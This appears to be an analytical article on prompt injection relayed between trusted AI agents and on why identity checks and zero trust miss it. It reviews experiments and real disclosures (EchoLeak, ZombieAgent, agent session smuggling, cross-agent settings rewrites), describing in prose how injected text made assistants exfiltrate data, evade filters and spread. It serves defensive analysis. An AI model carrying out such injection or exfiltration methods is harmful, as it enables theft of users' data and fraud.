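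A passed check can do harm if it leads people to relax other defences. Suppose the company has a content filter that catches half of all harmful messages. With the filter alone, 5 of the 10 get through. If the company then adds authentication and exempts authenticated peers from the filter to save time, 8 get through. If it applied both to every message, 4 would get through. The orchestrator that Paul and Nandy describe mistakenly treats a trusted sender as a reason to skip checks, and forwards a compliance agent's approval without checking it again.

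### The same gap in email

Email has had sender authentication for years, and there is data on what it does and doesn't stop. It relies on three standards, SPF, DKIM and DMARC. With SPF, the owner of a domain publishes a list of the servers that may send its mail. With DKIM, the sending system signs each message with a key that belongs to a domain. Both checks can pass for a domain other than the one the recipient sees in the "From" line. DMARC therefore requires a message to pass at least one of them for the visible domain or another domain belonging to the same organisation.

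The current version of the standard, *Domain-Based Message Authentication, Reporting, and Conformance (DMARC)* (Herr and Levine, 2026), states that the domain owner's authorisation "does not carry an explicit or implicit value assertion about that message" and lists content analysis as out of scope. A pass is still useful because it lets the receiver reliably attribute the message to the domain and take the domain's reputation into account. This works well against domains that send mostly spam, but it does much less against one bad message from an organisation with a good record.

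Attackers can take over an employee's mailbox and send phishing emails from the genuine account, which researchers call lateral phishing. In *Detecting and Characterizing Lateral Phishing at Scale*, Ho, Cidon and colleagues (2019) studied 113 million emails sent by employees of 92 organisations. They found 1,902 lateral phishing emails from 154 hijacked accounts at 33 organisations. Some organisations were in the study because they had already reported such attacks, but of the 69 that the researchers picked at random, 10 had at least one incident within seven months.

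The researchers treated passing SPF or DKIM as one sign that a phishing email came from a hijacked account rather than from an outsider.

At least 17 of the 154 attackers took over another colleague's account, and Ho and colleagues consider this an underestimate. The median success rate was low, at one new account for every 542 colleagues targeted. In one case, recipients replied to ask whether the email was genuine, but the attacker controlled the account and answered them from it.

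The behaviour of the hijacked accounts did help to expose these attacks. In the early part of the data, 95 percent of the accounts sent phishing emails to 25 or more people. Ho and colleagues built a detector that used the number of recipients among other features, and it found 87.3 percent of the attacks with fewer than four false alarms per million emails. The false alarm rate had to be that low because only about one email in 59,000 was lateral phishing. A detector that wrongly flagged 1 percent of emails, the low end of the range they give for an earlier system, would have raised around 600 false alarms for each real attack. The number of recipients would not help Payments, however, because the Reader sends its summary to one recipient, as it does every morning.

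The comparison with email is inexact because lateral phishing requires a hijacked account. That makes it more like stealing the Reader's credentials, and the organisation can end it by resetting a password. The attack through the Reader is more like an honest colleague forwarding a fake invoice they believed was real. There is no credential to reset because the attacker hasn't taken over anything, and in that respect the problem is harder for agents.

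A rough figure from Cloudflare, which sells email security, is that 89 percent of unwanted email in general passed the authentication checks. If nearly all wanted email passes too, the last fraction in Bayes' rule is about 0.9, so a pass hardly changes the odds that a message is unwanted. The fraud in the Payments example is growing even with human victims. APWG's *Phishing Activity Trends Report, 2nd Quarter 2026* (2026) records an 88 percent rise in email attacks that seek a wire transfer, with attackers asking for $61,732 per attempt. That count doesn't separate hijacked accounts from impersonation.

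### Whether zero trust already covers this

People who work on zero trust could fairly object that they never held the view criticised here. *Zero Trust Architecture* (Rose, Borchert and colleagues, 2020), the NIST standard from the last section, requires much more than a verified identity. It tells organisations to assume that an attacker is already present, to grant only the privileges each task needs, and to keep re-evaluating trust after access begins. It even anticipates the confused deputy, warning that an attacker might trick a software agent that manages security systems into performing a task that the attacker has no right to perform.

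These principles do reduce the damage. Dantuluri and Sundi tested least privilege with a program that sits between agents and their tools, gives each agent a token limited to its subtask, and checks every call without consulting the model. They simulated 2,000 random delegations in an environment with 8,100 possible actions. A compromised sub-agent could perform all 8,100 with an ordinary broad token, but only 1.5 on average with the limited one. Both work for VotalAI, which sells a product built on the same principles, but one would expect this result from any properly enforced restriction.

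They require that a fully hijacked agent not exceed the authority delegated to it. The attack on Payments stays within that authority. Changing a supplier's account number may be one of the very few actions Payments can still take, and it is the only one the attacker needs. The company could remove that action too and have a person make every change. That would be a good decision for many companies, but Payments would no longer do that part of its job.

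Continuous evaluation has a similar limit. Rose and colleagues acknowledge that a system that judges each request in isolation can miss an attack that stays within the requester's allowed role. Considering recent behaviour helps when the attack is conspicuous, as when someone in human resources who normally opens 20 to 30 employee records a day opens more than 100. A single change of account number does not stand out in this way.

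Others have extended zero trust to cover content. Valenzuela, in *The Agent Identity Problem*, an article for the security training organisation SANS, accepts that a compromised agent can pass checks on the user, the device and the source. He proposes three further layers of defence:

- inspecting content before the agent processes it
- checking every action against a scope that the organisation defined in advance
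- planting honey tokens, which are decoys that no legitimate task would touch

Valenzuela's example is a vendor contract with hidden instructions to collect credentials and post them to an outside address. Those actions are outside the scope of an agent that reads documents and returns summaries, so the scope check would block them. In the Payments case, the change of account is within scope and the attack doesn't touch a decoy. Only content inspection could stop it, and Valenzuela warns that organisations should assume attackers will get past that layer.

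*Fortifying the Agentic Web* (Huang, Mehmood and colleagues, 2025) goes further and redesigns zero trust for agents. It lists communication between agents among the ways malicious instructions can get into an agent's memory. In its model, each memory entry has a source and a trust score, and the architecture includes audits of the chain of causes behind an action. This comes closest to what Payments lacks, but it helps Payments only if the source field names the stranger's email and not just the Reader.

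The objection is right about the principles of zero trust, but a policy decision that rests on the subject and the resource still can't distinguish an honest request from a fraudulent one. Suppose Harlow really changes banks one morning, and on another morning an attacker pretends that it has. The policy engine receives two requests from the same agent, acting for the same employee, for the same kind of change to the same record. Both agents' machines are healthy, and the account number is new in both cases. A rule that works from these facts must give both requests the same answer. It can refuse both, which stops honest suppliers from updating their details this way, or allow both.

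Rose and colleagues list the inputs to a decision, and none of them records who originally supplied the content of a request. Their definition of zero trust does allow for such an input, since it lets policies use other attributes of behaviour and environment. A company could treat the origin of an account number as one of these attributes and refuse any change that traces back to an unverified email. But some component has to supply the attribute, and by the time the summary reaches Payments, it no longer includes the account number's origin.

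## Experiments on harmful instructions passed between trusted agents

Whether an email can redirect a payment depends on how the models behind the Reader and Payments respond to text. Researchers have found success rates from zero to 100 percent for such attacks, partly because they measured different parts of the attack, which has five stages.

| Stage | In the Payments example |
| --- | --- |
| Entry | The attacker's email reaches the Reader's context |
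| Acceptance by the first agent | The Reader's model believes the hidden text or follows it |
| Relay | The Reader includes the new account number in its message to Payments |
| Acceptance by the next agent | Payments' model takes the change to be genuine |
| Action | Payments calls the tool that updates the record |

The attack works only if every stage does, so its overall success rate is a product:

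$$P(\text{attack}) = P(E)\,P(A_1 \mid E)\,P(R \mid A_1)\,P(A_2 \mid R)\,P(X \mid A_2)$$

Here E is entry, A₁ and A₂ are acceptance by the two agents, R is relay and X is the action. If the email always gets in and each later stage succeeds 70 percent of the time, the whole attack succeeds about 24 percent of the time. A researcher who plants the instruction in the first agent's system prompt skips one of those later stages and would report 34 percent for the same system.

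Work on such attacks goes back to 2024. Cohen, Bitton and Nassi built prompts that copied themselves between email assistants (Morris II), and Lee and colleagues had malicious prompts replicate across connected agents (Prompt Infection). Both studies used models that are long out of date. In most later experiments with several agents, the harmful message came from the agent named as its sender, so mutual TLS or a signature would have let it through.

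### The same command from a user, a document and a peer

Lupinacci, Pironti and colleagues (2025), in *The Dark Side of LLMs*, tried to get agents to install malware on a Linux machine. They tested 18 models, including GPT-4.1, Claude 4 Opus and Gemini 2.5 Pro. They delivered the command in three ways: the user typed it, the agent retrieved a document that contained it in tiny white text, or one agent retrieved the document and asked a second agent, which had terminal access, to run the command.

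| Source of the command | Models that ran it at least once |
| --- | --- |
| User | 17 of 18 (94.4%) |
| Retrieved document | 15 of 18 (83.3%) |
| Peer agent | 18 of 18 (100%) |

Llama 4 refused the command when it came from the user or the document, while Gemini 2.5 Pro and Llama 3.3 refused it only when it came from the document. All three models ran the command when a peer agent sent it. Lupinacci and colleagues conclude that models treat peer agents as inherently trustworthy.

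The 100 percent figure uses a lenient definition of vulnerability. A model counted as vulnerable if even one attempt succeeded, and each model faced six versions of the prompt with up to three runs of each. But this definition doesn't explain the whole difference between peer messages and documents. The most effective version for peer messages succeeded on every model, while the most effective version for documents had a success rate of 78 percent.

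A bigger problem is that the text changed along with the sender. The user's prompt and the document surrounded the command with pressure, such as demands to act immediately or to ignore everything the model knew. The second agent received only the bare command, and its only job was to execute what the calling agent sent. The models that refused did so because they recognised the request as malicious, and the pressure may well have helped them recognise it. So the experiment shows that attacks sent through a peer agent work, but not that trust in peers is the reason.

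A follow-up test makes that explanation look less likely. The researchers gave three of the models a tool that could only ping a network address. When the attack came from the user or a document, all three slipped the attacker's extra command into the tool's input. When it came from a peer, none did, because they took only the address they needed from the message. With a different tool, a file search program that can also run other programs, the attack through a peer worked on all three again. This looks more like an agent doing its one job with whatever its tool allows than a general tendency to follow peers. Payments could still be at risk, because its job includes changing bank details.

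### Changing the sender without changing the text

*Only as Safe as the Weakest Agent* (Wang and Mannby, 2026) isolated the effect of the sender by delivering the same false report from different sources. The main agent adopted the report in 102 of 120 trials (85 percent) when it came as the result of a sub-agent, which the main agent had launched for part of its task, and in 18 of 39 trials (46 percent) when it came as a message from a peer. Claude Opus 4.6 and Sonnet 4.6 never adopted the report from a peer but did adopt it from a sub-agent. The peer sample is small, but the results suggest that models are more likely to accept an answer they requested than an unprompted message.

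In *Same Payload, Different Channel*, Syed and Yasaei (2026) gave ten open-weight models identical malicious instructions, either in the user's message or in material from a tool, with the same tools available in both cases. The instructions succeeded less often when they came through a tool, by an average of 12 percentage points for models that their makers advertise for agent work and 36 points for general-purpose models. Keeping the tools the same mattered because just making tools available raised the success rate of instructions in the user's message from 24.3 to 52.5 percent in the agent models.

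A2A lets developers decide how to present a peer's words to the model. This experiment is relevant to that choice, although it did not include a peer. Going by Syed and Yasaei's results, presenting the words as the user's own message would probably give them the most weight, and presenting them as tool output seems safer. In the agent models, attacks in a tool's output succeeded 6.7 percent of the time, compared with 53.3 percent for attacks in a tool's description, although the two figures come from different sets of cases.

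Attackers can also make their text look like the user's, an attack tested in *Understanding and Mitigating Role Spoofing in LLMs* (2026). The researchers first measured how often each model would perform a malicious task when the real user asked, then scaled the attack's success by that rate so that refusing the task itself would not count as resisting the impostor. In a simple test with tools, the attack succeeded more than 95 percent of the time on every model except Gemini 3.1 Pro, where it succeeded 72.5 percent of the time.

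Other experiments changed the name or status of an agent:

- *Trust the Brand, Lose Control* (2026) swapped the model families that an orchestrator saw next to its sub-agents. With truthful labels, the orchestrator obtained the risky response in 25.9 percent of tasks, and with the labels reversed, in 74.6 percent.
- *Do LLM Agents Mirror Socio-Cognitive Effects in Power-Asymmetric Conversations?* (2026) had agents of different status send each other unsafe requests. The lower-status agents were more likely to comply.
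- *Exploring the Hidden Cost of the World Around AI Agents* (2026) tested 16 models with messages that invoked authority. The agents acted on the requests at similar rates whoever the named sender was.

Wang and Mannby's data may help reconcile these results, because the effect of status varied greatly between models. They had an attacker contradict a model that could no longer see the original source. When the attacker was an expert instead of a peer, GPT-4o-mini's errors rose from 78 to 176 out of 180, and GPT-5.5's rose from 0 to 20. Claude Sonnet 4.6 made no errors with either attacker, and Llama 3.1 8B gave in to both almost every time.

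There is some evidence that AI agents favour other AI agents. In a social simulation, Wang, Gu and colleagues (*When Agents See Humans as the Outgroup*, 2026) found that agents favoured their own group, and that this could work against humans when an agent was unsure whether it was dealing with one. *LLMs Trust Their Own* (2026) reports that invented agreement among peers can steer a model's answers. Neither result establishes that a model will run a harmful command because a peer asked.

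The stated sender has a large effect on some models and almost none on others, and models don't always trust peer agents the most. A developer who labels a message as coming from a verified colleague could therefore make some models more likely to obey a request injected into it.

### False reports that contain no instruction

The hidden text in the Harlow email includes a statement that the supplier's account number is now 4471. Wang and Mannby's main experiment tested such false statements on the coding products Claude Code and Codex. They created a folder of files about fictional people and events, with one true record for each question and one or more forgeries that contradicted it. Most of the forgeries had two flaws that a careful reader could spot: they were dated earlier than the record they supposedly corrected, and they lacked a reference line that every genuine record had.

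In one condition, the product's strong main model searched the files itself. In the other, it had to send a cheaper sub-agent to read them and rely on its report. The table shows how many times out of 180 questions the main model ended up with the attacker's answer.

| Product and forgery | Strong model reads the files | Cheaper sub-agent reads them |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Code, a senior archivist's note | 1 | 20 |
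| Claude Code, several kinds of forgery together | 1 | 75 |
| Codex, a senior archivist's note | 0 | 44 |
| Claude Code, a correction notice without the flaws | 175 | 173 |
| Codex, a correction notice without the flaws | 180 | 180 |

Delegation alone did not cause the errors. With a sub-agent as strong as the main model, Claude Code made none on either of the first two forgeries, and Codex made one on the archivist's note. Wang and Mannby conclude that a system is about as safe as its weakest reader. That conclusion doesn't hold in the last two rows, where the forgery had no visible flaws and the strong models accepted it almost every time, even when they read it themselves. A better model in the Reader therefore wouldn't solve the problem of a well-made fake of a supplier's email.

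When the strong model read the group of forgeries itself, it remarked on the missing reference line in all 180 runs. Claude Code's logs show that the sub-agent's report to the main model mentioned it in only 96. The main model adopted the false claim in 21 of those 96 runs, and in 54 of the 84 where the report left the warning out. That fits the earlier argument that a summary loses the origin of a claim. But with the archivist's note, errors were not significantly more likely when the report omitted the warning, so the omission may not fully explain the errors.

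Explicit instructions to the model, the classic form of prompt injection, failed everywhere Wang and Mannby tried them. Training seems to have made these models less likely to follow commands in documents, but the forged records contained no commands.

They also simulated a longer chain, in which an attacker misled a worker agent and the worker reported to an aggregator that never saw the source. The aggregator repeated the error in 751 of the 757 cases where the worker was fooled. The aggregators included GPT-5.5 and Claude Opus 5, which are hard to mislead directly. When the researchers also gave the aggregators the original record, the aggregators made no errors in 780 trials. Payments is in the same position as the aggregator because it doesn't receive the original email.

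Attacks relayed between agents sometimes fail, in some cases only by luck. In *Agentic Societies Need a Social Harness* (2026), a student wanted a mutual acquaintance to host a gathering and invite a target, without revealing who was behind it. Often the student's own agent refused to send the request, or the acquaintance's agent never passed on the invitation. In another scenario, an adversary had several students' agents each ask a professor's agent about one day of the week, to piece together the whole calendar. The professor's agent disclosed the professor's availability and named the events in every run. The reconstruction failed only when agents garbled or lost the answers on the way back. Each question was harmless by itself, and no agent could see the other conversations.

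In Paul and Nandy's six-agent system, attacks that cascaded through the agents were no less effective than a direct attack. They succeeded 28 percent of the time, compared with 22 percent for an order typed straight to the orchestrator to override its instructions.

### Content that agents keep passing on

To reach an agent deep inside an organisation, an attacker may need content that each agent passes on in turn. *Mind Viruses* (Papadopoulos, Shah and colleagues, 2026) studied this with teams of six coding agents, which shared files, could message each other and ran for 30 turns each. The researchers wrote an ideology and a drive to spread it into one agent's system prompt, and allowed that agent only to send messages. To find effective wording, they had a language model rewrite the prompt over several generations and kept the versions that spread best.

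Each agent had a memory file. At the end of a run, the program warned the agents that it was about to wipe their contexts and gave them one last turn to write in their files. Another model then scored each file from 0 to 3 for signs of the ideology, and only a 3 counted as an infection. This strict test misses agents that go along with an idea without writing it down. In one condition, DeepSeek V3.2 was not counted because it didn't write to its memory, apparently because it lacked the skill.

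Harmful content spread less readily than harmless content. A call for AI to dominate humans spread in teams running DeepSeek V3.2, Qwen 3.5 32B and Gemini 3 Flash, but not in those running Claude Sonnet 4.6, GPT-5.4 or Claude Haiku 4.5. A love of whales spread even in Haiku teams, and the agents abandoned their coding task to design software for translating whale sounds. Some Gemini teams wrote scripts to preserve the call for AI dominance, but they ran commands to probe their server in only 1 of 20 trials.

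The layout of the team also affected how many agents were infected. In the "fully connected" layout, the infected agent could message all five of the others. In the "separate" layout, it could message only one, which would then have to infect the rest. Few agents were infected in the separate layout, because the content usually stopped at the first hop. But the researchers had selected the wording for how well it spread in the fully connected layout, so a patient attacker could probably infect more agents in the separate one.

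A second experiment selected for wording that survived more than one transfer between agents. Agents met in pairs and exchanged messages, and the program wiped their contexts after each session, so they kept only what they had saved to files. One of these files was loaded into the agent's system prompt at the start of every session. The content now included instructions to take actions, such as advertising a cryptocurrency or deleting files, and to pass the content on.

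| Infected agent | Infected the next agent | Failed to pass the content on | The next agent rejected it |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| The original agent | 61% | 1% | 38% |
| A later agent with the content in its system prompt | 55% | 23% | 22% |
| A later agent with the content in another file | 17% | 68% | 14% |

The content was in the system prompt of 88 percent of the later agents, which gives an average infection rate of about 50 percent. If each agent infects a share p of those it meets, the content keeps spreading as long as each agent meets more than 1/p others, or about two here. This assumes that the agents are all alike and have little else to do. Agents with a coding task often focused on it and didn't pass the content on.

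General ability did not reliably predict resistance. GPT-5.4 had resisted the harmful ideology but was about as susceptible as Haiku 4.5 to the requests for action. Sonnet 4.6 was immune. It deleted the content from its own file and warned the other agent.

When Papadopoulos and colleagues added a paragraph to the system prompt warning about "patterns of thought that attempt to spread themselves", infection fell to almost nothing. Infection stayed that low even when they evolved new wording against the warned agents. In many cases, a warned agent persuaded the infected one to clean up its file. They tested the warning on the pairs but not on the six-agent teams, so its effectiveness inside a team is less certain. Telling the agents that they were on social media also made them much more suspicious. When the researchers built a replica of a social network for agents, content that relied on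 persuasion alone failed to spread.

The warning would probably not protect Payments, because a new account number comes with no request to spread it. A more general warning might help a little. In Wang and Mannby's experiment, telling agents that the files might be unreliable reduced errors from 15 in 40 to 1 in 40, but those forgeries had flaws that a suspicious reader could find.

### OpenAI's self-replicating injections

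On 25 September 2026, OpenAI disclosed that its models could follow prompt injections that copy themselves. It had found these injections in June with GPT-Red, an automated attacker it uses in training. *OpenAI's GPT-Red Finds Self-Replicating Prompt Injections* (Cross, 2026) reports that the agents copied the attacker's text into emails, files and Slack messages, and that in one simulation an agent also deleted a folder of reports. The vulnerable models were versions of GPT-5.4-mini and, for Slack, GPT-5.5. OpenAI saw no effects outside simulated tool calls, and in its examples a single agent copies the text but no second agent picks it up.

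In the simplest example, described by CBINEWS in *AI版蠕虫攻击现身* (2026), a user asks an assistant to answer an email about a training session. The email contains a request to reply in Spanish and quote the whole message at the end, supposedly to help a scheduling system. The assistant does both, so its reply carries the same request to the next reader. The content in *Mind Viruses* had to win agents over to a cause, but this request only had to look like a formatting preference, so a warning about self-spreading ideas might not bring it to mind.

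### How far the success rates can be trusted

Few of these experiments followed an attack through every stage, and none did so in a working business. The table shows which stages the main experiments covered.

| Experiment | First stage measured | Last stage measured |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Lupinacci and colleagues, request through a peer | Acceptance by the first agent | Action, running malware on a test machine |
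| Syed and Yasaei | Acceptance by a single agent | Action, a simulated tool call |
| Wang and Mannby | Acceptance by the first agent | Acceptance by the next agent |
| Papadopoulos and colleagues | Relay by an agent that the researchers infected | Further relay, with action in some cases |
| OpenAI | Acceptance by the first agent | Relay, with simulated actions |

These experiments don't test how harmful text reaches an agent, because the researchers placed it where an agent would read it. Lupinacci and colleagues, for example, kept the whole prompt in one chunk of the document so that the agent was more likely to retrieve it. Wang and Mannby used real products, but the folders held invented files and the outcome was a wrong answer to a quiz question. An agent that repeats a false fact about a fictional archive might still refuse to change a bank account.

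The percentages that Lupinacci and colleagues reported are also a poor estimate of what a current model would do. All 18 models they tested date from 2024 and 2025, and developers have since worked hard to make models more resistant. OpenAI reports that GPT-5.6 Sol had six times fewer failures than an earlier model on its hardest benchmark for direct prompt injection. However, the experiments in which forged records fooled GPT-5.6 Sol and Claude Opus 5 are much more recent.

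Success rates also depend on the attacker's effort. Papadopoulos and colleagues found effective wording for some goals only after many generations, and never found any for stealing secrets from Haiku 4.5, though a better search might have. The programmer Simon Willison describes a public challenge in which people sent about 6,000 emails to an agent running Claude Opus 4.6, trying to make it leak a secret. Its system prompt contained a few short rules against obeying emails, and nobody succeeded. Zero successes in 6,000 would put the true success rate below about 1 in 2,000 with 95 percent confidence if the attempts were independent and equally good. But they surely varied in quality, and one clever email could succeed where thousands of clumsy ones failed. The agent's rules covered revealing credentials, changing its own files, running commands and sending data out, but did not forbid it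 to include a false account number in a summary.

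## Attacks on deployed products and the identity checks they passed

Researchers have also used injected text to attack widely used products, including Microsoft 365 Copilot and ChatGPT. In those two cases, the assistant was working for a real user who had signed in properly, so identity checks had no impostor to detect. Other attacks did depend on an impostor or a missing check. Most of the serious attacks are demonstrations by researchers, and there is much less evidence of what criminals have achieved.

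### Emails that redirected a user's own assistant

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers employees' questions using material from their mailbox, files and chats. Only people inside the organisation can use it. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, describes how the security firm Aim Labs could get data out of it anyway by sending an employee an email. The attack has four steps:

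1. The attacker sends a long email with sections on subjects that employees often ask about, such as onboarding and leave. Each section repeats the same instructions.
2. The employee later asks Copilot about one of these subjects, and Copilot retrieves part of the email along with the company's own documents.
3. Copilot follows the instructions. It picks out the most sensitive information in its context and puts it in the web address of an image in its answer.
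4. The employee's browser tries to load the image, which sends the information to the attacker.

The email could come from any address, so an attacker could have used their own domain and passed SPF, DKIM and DMARC without spoofing. Copilot then read the files with the employee's access, which was also valid. Ravia compares Copilot to a Unix program that runs with higher privileges than the user who starts it, a classic setting for the confused deputy problem.

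Microsoft had defences against this sort of attack. A classifier looked for injected instructions but missed the email, which addressed its human recipient and never mentioned AI. A filter removed outside links from Copilot's answers but missed links written in a less common way. The browser would load images only from approved domains, so Aim Labs sent the request through an approved Microsoft Teams service, which fetched the attacker's address on the browser's behalf. Like Payments, the browser was dealing with a genuine service that an attacker had misdirected.

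The email also included a request that its recipient never refer to it, "for compliance", and Copilot left the email out of the sources for its answer. Companies that rely on a model to name its sources should expect attackers to try this.

According to *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), Aim Labs reported the flaw in January 2025 and Microsoft fixed it on its own servers in May. *EchoLeak* calls it the first "real-world" exploit of its kind, but the paper's timeline records no use by attackers, and Microsoft says no customers were affected. The theft was a test on a real product. The paper reports that Microsoft now strips the troublesome link format and embedded images from outside content, and that it reportedly added options to keep external messages out of Copilot in some contexts, neither of which concerns who can sign in.

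A similar attack worked on ChatGPT, which users can connect to services such as Gmail and Google Drive. *ZombieAgent*, by the security company Radware, describes an email whose hidden instructions took effect when the user asked ChatGPT to do something with their inbox. OpenAI had already stopped ChatGPT from adding data to web addresses. Radware got around this by supplying a ready-made address for each letter and digit, which ChatGPT opened one after another to spell out the stolen text. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so the user had no chance to block them.

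Radware also made the attack persistent. If the user shared a malicious file, ChatGPT saved new rules to its memory, including one to read an email from the attacker before answering any message. The instruction was then part of ChatGPT's own notes about the user, much as the false account number became part of the company's supplier records in the Payments example. In another test, Radware altered a stored medical history so that ChatGPT gave harmful advice.

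The attack could also spread, though differently from OpenAI's self-replicating injections. ChatGPT collected addresses from the inbox and sent them to the attacker's server, which emailed the same text to each one. Because these emails came from the attacker, not the victim's account, a rule that accepted mail only from known senders could have stopped the spread. Radware reported the flaws on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed them 81 days later.

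Fixes like these block particular attacks, but researchers keep finding others. SC Media's *New attack bypasses AI guardrails by encrypting malicious prompts* (2026) reports that a researcher at the security firm Adversa got Grok, the assistant from Elon Musk's AI company, to leak users' personal data when users asked it to summarise a web page. The page contained encrypted instructions, which filters missed and Grok decrypted. The developer had known about the problem since June, but Grok was still leaking data in August. In the same week, researchers got Microsoft 365 Copilot to reveal a password.

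### Attacks from one agent on another

In the attacks on Copilot and ChatGPT, a single assistant read the attacker's text directly. Unit 42, the threat research team of Palo Alto Networks, demonstrated an attack between two agents that communicate over A2A. The team built a financial assistant that could see a user's portfolio and buy shares, and a malicious research assistant that supplied market news. When the user asked for a briefing, the financial assistant passed the request to the research assistant, which sent additional messages before returning the news.

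In one test, the other agent's messages looked like clarifying questions, and the financial assistant gradually revealed its instructions, its list of tools and the user's earlier conversation. In another, the assistant bought 10 shares that the user had not asked for. A user with an ordinary chat window would probably have seen only the final news summary. Unit 42 calls the technique agent session smuggling. It found no flaw in A2A itself and has not seen attackers use the technique.

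This attack differs from the Payments example because the sending agent was malicious, not deceived, so identity checks can do more. A registry of vetted agents might have kept the research assistant out. A signed Agent Card would help less, since an attacker who runs an agent can sign a valid card for it. Unit 42 recommends signed cards against impersonation but accepts that they don't stop someone from subverting a trusted agent. It considers human approval the most effective defence, provided the request appears somewhere the model cannot influence.

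Okta, which sells identity software, draws a different lesson, emphasising narrow permissions and a cryptographic record of delegation. Narrow permissions would have blocked the purchase, because preparing a news briefing doesn't require buying shares. The record would mostly have helped after the purchase had been made.

The closest parallel to the Reader and Payments comes from coding assistants. Willison (2025) describes work by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, who had earlier shown that injected text could get GitHub Copilot to edit its own settings and turn off requests for the user's approval. Developers of such agents responded by blocking such changes. Rehberger then pointed out that many programmers run two agents on one computer. Text that hijacks GitHub Copilot can get it to rewrite the settings of Claude Code, which the programmer then starts, unaware of the change. *Cross-Agent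 Attack* (maximalfocus, 2025) includes a diagram in which the second agent then runs the attacker's code, and a loop of further escalation follows.

Both agents are genuine here, but outside text has tricked the first into misdirecting the second. The message between them is a settings file. Both agents run under the programmer's account, so the operating system treats the change as a user editing their own files and allows it. Separate accounts for the two agents would help only with settings stored outside the project folder, because both agents need to edit that folder. Kaplan (2026), in *Privilege Escalation via Confused Deputies in Coding Agents*, found the same technique independently and argues that it remains effective even as agents get better at protecting themselves.

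| Attack | Where the text entered | Whose access the agent used | Why identity checks passed | Response |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| EchoLeak | An email from any outside address | The employee's | The employee had signed in and could read the files | Microsoft fixed it in May 2025 |
| ZombieAgent | An email or a shared file | The ChatGPT user's, including linked services | The user had signed in and linked the services | OpenAI fixed it in December 2025 |
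| Agent session smuggling | Extra messages from a malicious agent | The financial assistant's user's | The malicious agent used its own identity | Unit 42 recommends approval outside the model |
| Cross-agent privilege escalation | Material that a coding agent reads | The programmer's | Both agents ran under one account | Agents can no longer edit their own settings, but others still can |

Files in software projects have remained a common way to attack agents. AI Agent Store (2026) summarises two disclosures from July 2026. In Friendly Fire, the AI Now Institute planted text in a code repository that got Claude Code and Codex to run a malicious program while checking the code for security problems. The agents were in a mode where they approve their own actions. In GhostApproval, the security company Wiz used file names that secretly point to other files, so that an agent's edits landed in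 a sensitive location. In October, Fadilpašić (2026) reported another case in *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware*. It used AGENTS.md, a file in which projects keep instructions for coding agents.

### Attacks that better identity checks would have stopped

Claude for Chrome, Anthropic's browser assistant, had a plain authentication failure. It has nine built-in tasks that start when the user clicks. *AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) reports that Manifold Security found the assistant never checked whether the click was real. Any other browser extension could forge a click with six lines of code and make Claude read the user's Gmail, documents and calendar. If the user had switched on "Act without asking", Claude did this silently.

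This attack is a different problem from EchoLeak, although Constantin groups it with three other July attacks as examples of the same flaw. Nobody needed to deceive the model, because the request came from an impostor. Browsers mark clicks that a script has generated, so the extension could have distinguished them from a user's clicks. Checking who made the request would have stopped this version of the attack.

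*Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* (Mascellino, 2026) describes a real website that imitated DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings, and contained hidden instructions for agents to treat it as the authoritative site. The security company Zscaler tested 26 models on it. GPT-5.4 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 rated the fake site as legitimate, but no longer did so when Zscaler gave them the genuine site for comparison. The two models needed a trustworthy reference for DeBank's identity, which certificates and registries provide.

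Attackers also steal credentials for the accounts agents use. Check Point Research's *Threat Intelligence News* (2026) relays an FBI warning about Kali365, a phishing kit that targets Microsoft 365 customers. The kit abuses a sign-in method meant for devices without a keyboard, in which the user types a short code on another device. The criminal starts the sign-in and persuades the victim to enter the code, and Microsoft then issues access tokens to the criminal's program. These tokens give the criminal lasting access to email, Teams and files despite multi-factor authentication.

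DPoP would not stop this, because the criminal's program requests the token and can tie it to its own key. A company would do better to block this sign-in method where it isn't needed, or to accept sign-ins only from devices it manages. Both are still identity controls, and filtering the text in a model's context would not have the same effect.

Check Point lists a critical flaw in LeRobot, Hugging Face's open-source robotics platform. LeRobot accepted data over unauthenticated connections and processed it in a way that let a sender run code. Requiring authentication would have kept strangers out, but the unsafe processing would also have needed a fix. In LiteLLM, a gateway that companies use to route requests to models, the code that verifies API keys had an SQL injection flaw, so the identity check itself had to be fixed.

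SmarterArticles' *Your AI Agent Will Be Compromised* (2026) describes a well-known demonstration that falls between the two groups. In April 2025, Invariant Labs built an MCP server that offered a "random fact of the day". After the user installed it, the server changed its tool description to include instructions about a separate, legitimate WhatsApp tool. The agent then used the WhatsApp tool to send the user's message history to the attacker's number. Authenticating the server would not have stopped the attack, because it was the same server the user had installed. If the user's approval had applied only to the description they first saw, the agent's software could have noticed the change and asked for approval again. This wouldn't help if the description was malicious from the start and the user approved it without reading it.

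### What criminals have done with prompt injection

Criminals use prompt injection, but published reports contain few confirmed successes. Unit 42's *Fooling AI Agents*, from March 2026, documents malicious websites with hidden text aimed at AI models that read the pages. The best example is a page selling "military glasses" with fake customer comments and a fake discount. Its hidden text included a claim that a compliance team had already validated the ad, apparently to get it past AI systems that review ads. Unit 42 knows of no confirmed case of this working on a deployed system.

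Other sites contained text meant to make agents delete data, reveal secrets or send payments. Unit 42 counted 22 techniques for building and hiding such text. It rated each attack by what the attacker seemed to want, because defenders can rarely see whether an injection succeeded. An attack rated "critical" may therefore have done no harm.

Zscaler found another campaign that used a page posing as documentation for a Python library. Hidden text on the page said that coding agents had to buy a $3 licence key to fix an error, and explained how to pay the attacker in cryptocurrency. In Zscaler's tests, 4 of the 26 models paid, including versions of Llama and Gemini. Those payments took place in a sandbox, so they don't show that anyone's agent paid in the real campaign.

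More attacks may follow, because criminals can now buy tools for them. Proofpoint's *Notes from Underground* describes advertisements on closed forums for programs that put injections into emails, PDFs, calendar invitations and web pages, with subscriptions from about $150 a month. One program writes the instructions in white text on a white background, like the Harlow email. The calendar version may need no action from the victim, because the invitation appears in their calendar before they accept it and an assistant may then summarise it.

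Proofpoint calls these tools experimental and says most reporting on prompt injection still comes from research and speculation. It suspects that criminals have had little reason to change their methods while deceiving people works so well. That seems plausible, but Proofpoint sells protection against such attacks, so its forecast of an imminent rise deserves some caution. The same caution applies to most companies that publish this research.

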